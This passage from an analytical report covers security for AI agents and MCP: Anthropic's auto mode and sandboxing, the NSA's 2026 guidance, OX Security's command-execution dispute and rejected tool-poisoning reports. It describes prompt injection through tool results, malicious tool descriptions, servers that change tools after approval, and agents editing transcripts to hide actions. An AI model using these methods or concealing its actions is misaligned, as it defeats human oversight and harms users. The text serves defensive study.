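Claude's lead is large, but the test shows little about what auto mode contributes, since the models resisted almost every attack without it. The Codex results are clearer evidence for automatic review, which cut successful attacks by about 69%. The testers used their own browser tools with both agents, without the protections in either company's browser extension. OpenAI had released a new version of Auto-review by the time Anthropic published the results.

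Cowork has a stricter default than Claude Code. It runs Claude's code in a virtual machine that can reach only the folders the user selects. Anthropic's reason is that developers can usually judge shell commands, while office workers can't be expected to. But the study of testers weakens this argument, because people who can understand a command may still approve it without reading it. Developers would therefore benefit from isolation by default too.

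### What the log shows

Claude Code keeps a transcript of each session on the developer's machine. An agent that could edit this transcript could hide what it had done, as some of OpenAI's agents did on a small scale in July. Auto mode blocks changes to transcripts, and the sandbox stops shell commands from altering most of the folder that contains them.

Anthropic notes that after an injection through a tool result succeeds, the log shows a successful, authorised call and no sign of the attack. Anthropic therefore prefers to inspect results before the model reads them. In auto mode, a separate check scans results for hidden instructions and adds a warning if it finds any.

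Anthropic's statement is true of a log that contains only calls. If the log also includes tool results, an investigator could find the upload address in the bug report, though this wouldn't prove that the report caused the call. Jin and colleagues propose that the host also record each permission decision in a trace that it can replay. In the example, the trace would show whether a rule, the developer or the classifier allowed the upload.

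Isolation can make monitoring harder. The virtual machine around Cowork also keeps out the security software that companies use to monitor their computers. Administrators can export Cowork's event logs, but by then the upload will have finished.

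## The NSA's 2026 guidance and the dispute over who must secure a call

Anthropic makes both Claude Code and the model inside it, so it can add safeguards at every step from the model to the shell. Most agents combine parts from several organisations: a model, an agent framework, an MCP library, a host application and outside tools. When a harmful call gets through, each organisation can argue that another should have stopped it. In 2026, security agencies published advice on who should check what. Researchers also reported specific weaknesses to several suppliers, most of whom replied that the check should happen elsewhere.

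### The NSA's criticisms

The NSA announced an information sheet on MCP on 20 May (NSA, 2026). In it, the agency compares MCP with early web protocols, because MCP's flexible design gave developers freedom but left them unsure how to use it safely. The agency's main complaint is that MCP's security depends more on each implementer's discipline than on guarantees in the protocol.

The guidance lists eight concerns, including weak access control and servers that an attacker can overload with needlessly complex tasks. Another is that servers often fail to keep data from separate tasks apart. In the NSA's example, a developer deploys a simple weather server without restrictions, and someone later adapts it to process sensitive information about people at a location.

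In an MCP tool call, the client sends a request and the server acts on it, as on the web. The NSA's criticism that MCP reverses this familiar pattern is loosely worded, because it fits only the features that let a server request information from the client or its user.

The sheet judges the version of November 2025. The July 2026 revision changed some of what it criticises:

| The NSA's criticism | After the July revision |
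|---|---|
| Authorization is optional | It is still optional |
| An attacker who takes over a session can pose as the client | The protocol no longer has sessions, but a thief can still use a stolen access token |
| MCP doesn't make repeated calls harmless | Each tool still has to recognise duplicates, and a client must now resend a call if the reply breaks off |
| A server can change after approval without new consent | Clients still need not ask again |
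| Many implementations keep poor logs or none | Linked records now have standard field names, but logging is still only a recommendation |

On repeated calls, the revision may have increased the risk.

### What the NSA recommends

The NSA makes nine recommendations and says that organisations can carry out most of them with ordinary software such as proxies and sandboxes. It advises them to choose servers that are still maintained, because the MCP project has archived many popular ones. They should separate tools for public data from tools for sensitive data, and use the operating system to limit what each tool can reach. Each call's arguments should match the schema, fall within the expected range and suit the context. Logs should include the exact arguments, the identities involved and, where feasible, a hash of the result. The NSA also advises companies to scan their own networks for unapproved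 MCP servers.

Two of the recommendations offer limited protection. The NSA wants sensitive messages to have cryptographic signatures and expiry times, which would stop an outsider from altering a message or replaying it later, but a malicious supplier could still sign a false result. The NSA also recommends scanning tool results for forbidden keywords and hidden instructions, but an attacker can reword an instruction to avoid detection. The NSA concedes that security proxies designed for MCP are immature and advises caution with them.

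Much of this work requires a security team. The owner of the small firm in the invoice example could choose a maintained server, but she probably couldn't review its code or set up a separate sandbox for each tool.

### Joint advice on outside tools

The NSA had announced broader guidance on 30 April, written with agencies from Australia, Canada, New Zealand, the United Kingdom and the United States (NSA, 2026). *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (Australian Signals Directorate, 2026) addresses its advice on third-party components mainly to developers and vendors. It advises them to keep a registry of trusted components, allow only approved tools and versions, and check these regularly. Organisations that run agents can use the same list when choosing a product.

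The agencies warn that agents choose tools with persuasive descriptions more often, and they recommend a standard format without persuasive language. But the supplier normally writes the description, so a developer who follows this advice has to reject a persuasive one or rewrite it, as TRUSTDESC does.

A fictitious case in the guidance shows why approval at installation isn't enough. An organisation adds an outside scheduling component to its customer support agent and grants broad access at start-up. When an attacker takes over the component, the agent keeps relying on the old permission decisions. The attacker reaches customer accounts, and then the agents that handle billing and refunds. The agencies recommend rechecking identity and permission for each request. They also want designers or operators, rather than the agent, to decide which actions need a person's approval.

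Their strictest advice is to use agents only for low-risk, non-sensitive tasks. Recording a supplier's bank details probably wouldn't qualify. The NSA's May sheet includes instructions for processing private data through MCP. The two documents are compatible if the second is meant for organisations that have decided to take the risk, but neither explains how to make that decision.

Suppliers of online services also have to protect themselves from their customers' agents. In August, the Australian Signals Directorate (2026) advised them to consider that agents might find and exploit vulnerabilities "at speed and scale".

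### OX Security's dispute with Anthropic

MCP's official libraries start a local server by running a command from the host's configuration. In April 2026, OX Security's *The Mother of All AI Supply Chains* called this design a critical vulnerability. The libraries run the command without checking that it is safe. If only the machine's owner can edit the configuration, this gives the owner no new power. But some web applications let their users supply the configuration, and those users may be able to run commands on the application's server.

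OX says it ran commands on six live services this way. It estimates that the affected software has been downloaded more than 150 million times, that over 7,000 servers are publicly accessible, and that up to 200,000 instances are vulnerable. The download count doesn't show how many applications accept configuration from outsiders, and OX doesn't explain in its announcement how it arrived at 200,000. The flaws it found in named products are better evidence. It lists ten products, three of them already patched, although two of the ten share a CVE number. OX also sells software that detects the problem, so it has a commercial interest in the finding.

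Anthropic told OX that the behaviour was expected. In a statement quoted in ITPro's *AI agents using Anthropic MCP could be a vector*, it said, "We do not consider this a valid security vulnerability", because the user has to approve the change to the configuration file. Anthropic later updated its security policy to advise caution with local servers and to say that developers are responsible for securing their code.

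This answer works fairly well for a coding agent on a developer's laptop, where the person who approves the change also owns the machine. OX names several such agents as vulnerable, including Claude Code, but reports that only one, Windsurf, could be exploited without any action by the user. The answer doesn't work for a web application, because a stranger's approval doesn't protect the company whose server runs the command. But the application's developer chose to accept commands from strangers. The library has to start programs, and nothing in a command shows who wrote it.

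OX replies that "developers are not security engineers" and that tens of thousands of them can't each be expected to discover the danger. The MCP project doesn't deny the danger, and Cantina's *MCP stdio code execution risk* notes that the project's guidance calls for explicit consent, transparency and sandboxing when a user sets up a local server. The two sides disagree about whether the library should run any command by default or only those the developer has permitted.

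flyingpenguin's *Ox Security Report*, a blog post that strongly criticises Anthropic, lists four changes that OX proposed:

- run only servers that a manifest declares in advance, instead of arbitrary commands;
- block high-risk programs by default with a list of permitted commands;
- require developers to turn on a "dangerous mode" before a command can include changing input;
- require marketplaces to verify developers and their signed manifests.

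A list of permitted commands may protect less than OX suggests. Upsonic, a product in OX's own table, had such a list, and an attacker could bypass it through the arguments of a permitted program. The proposed dangerous mode is more convincing. It would break some existing applications until their developers changed a setting, but it would make those developers notice the risk. Some developers would turn the mode on without thinking, just as some users approve every prompt.

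Anthropic was also no longer solely responsible for the protocol. Tom's Hardware's *Anthropic's Model Context Protocol has critical security flaw exposed* notes that Anthropic had donated MCP to the Agentic AI Foundation the previous December. The project's position is close to Anthropic's. The Model Context Protocol security policy lists attacks between a client and the local server it starts among the intentional behaviours that don't count as vulnerabilities.

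### Five rejected reports

Shaikh and Montaruli, who found that none of the frameworks they tested deliberately checks tool descriptions, sent five reports to four organisations. All five were rejected. The replies are known from the researchers' account:

| Software | Type of problem reported | Reason for rejecting the report |
|---|---|---|
| MCP's software development kit | A server changes a tool after approval | Protection comes from "host-side review of tool calls" |
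| LangChain | The library doesn't check the authenticity of MCP data | It should pass the data on exactly as it is |
| LangChain | The library skips the schema check on arguments for MCP tools | It is "functioning as intended" |
| Microsoft's AutoGen | A tool's schema changes | The attacker must already control the server, and AutoGen documents servers as trusted |
| deepset's Haystack | Tool poisoning | Users should vet outside servers as they would any other third-party service |

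Shaikh and Montaruli conclude that the developers of each layer leave the problem to those of another. They interpret LangChain's position as leaving validation to the model's provider, although the replies they quote don't name anyone. Only deepset promised a change, which was to clarify its documentation on the trust Haystack places in servers.

The library developers have a good argument about tool descriptions, because the researchers' own scanner missed more than half of the attack scenarios and flagged some legitimate tools. A general-purpose library also can't distinguish a malicious rule about bank accounts from a company's real policy.

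That reasoning doesn't apply to the other reports. Software can check whether a call's arguments match a schema, or whether a tool's definition has changed, without understanding what either means. In all twelve set-ups, the agent fetches the tool list at most once per session, so Shaikh and Montaruli expect such checks to add negligible delay. Detecting a change between sessions would also require stored hashes.

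They also want MCP to require a label that separates plain descriptions from instructions. This proposal is weaker because the supplier would write the label, and a malicious supplier could mark an instruction as a description.

### What users can be expected to check

deepset's comparison with other third-party services understates the user's difficulty. An ordinary weather service returns data to a program that its developer has already written. An MCP weather tool also brings a description that can influence the model's use of other tools, and many users never see it.

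Microsoft is right that the attacker has to control a server, but a server can become malicious after the user has approved it, as postmark-mcp did.

The MCP project's answer is to review the calls. This relies on human approval, but most testers in Anthropic's study approved a clearly dangerous command, and a wrong account number is much harder to spot.

A fairer division of responsibility would give each party the checks it can perform. Libraries can enforce schemas and report changed definitions. Host applications can hold back a changed tool and limit its access. Suppliers can announce changes and request fewer permissions. The user or the company can then decide whether a tool is worth the remaining risk. The MCP project has started to look at one part of this. According to its site, the scope of its Security Interest Group includes ways to establish that a server is what it claims to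 be before a client uses it.

### Guidance, contracts and law

Neither the NSA's sheet nor the joint guidance is a law. The NSA provides its sheet without warranties and wrote it primarily to protect US national security systems, the military and defence contractors. The joint guidance states that it isn't legal advice, and the agencies accept no liability for losses from relying on it.

The joint guidance tells organisations to define legal accountability and risk ownership in their own policies. The firm in the invoice example could use such a policy to decide which employee is accountable for a wrong payment. But its policy can't bind the accounting service or the model's developer, so the firm would have to rely on a contract or the law. Neither document sets out what any country's law requires of developers, deployers or tool suppliers.

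Shaikh and Montaruli write that no model provider contractually guarantees resistance to prompt injection. They also claim that no market or regulatory incentive leads organisations at any layer to invest in defence. Their main evidence for this is the five replies, which only show how the organisations classify security reports. A company that declines to call something a vulnerability may still have obligations to its customers under a contract or general law.

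A contract with the accounting service could require notice before a tool changes and specify who pays for a wrong transfer and how long each side keeps its logs, which would matter in any dispute. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners warn that when several agents handle a payment, fragmented records can make it hard to tell which component caused the error.
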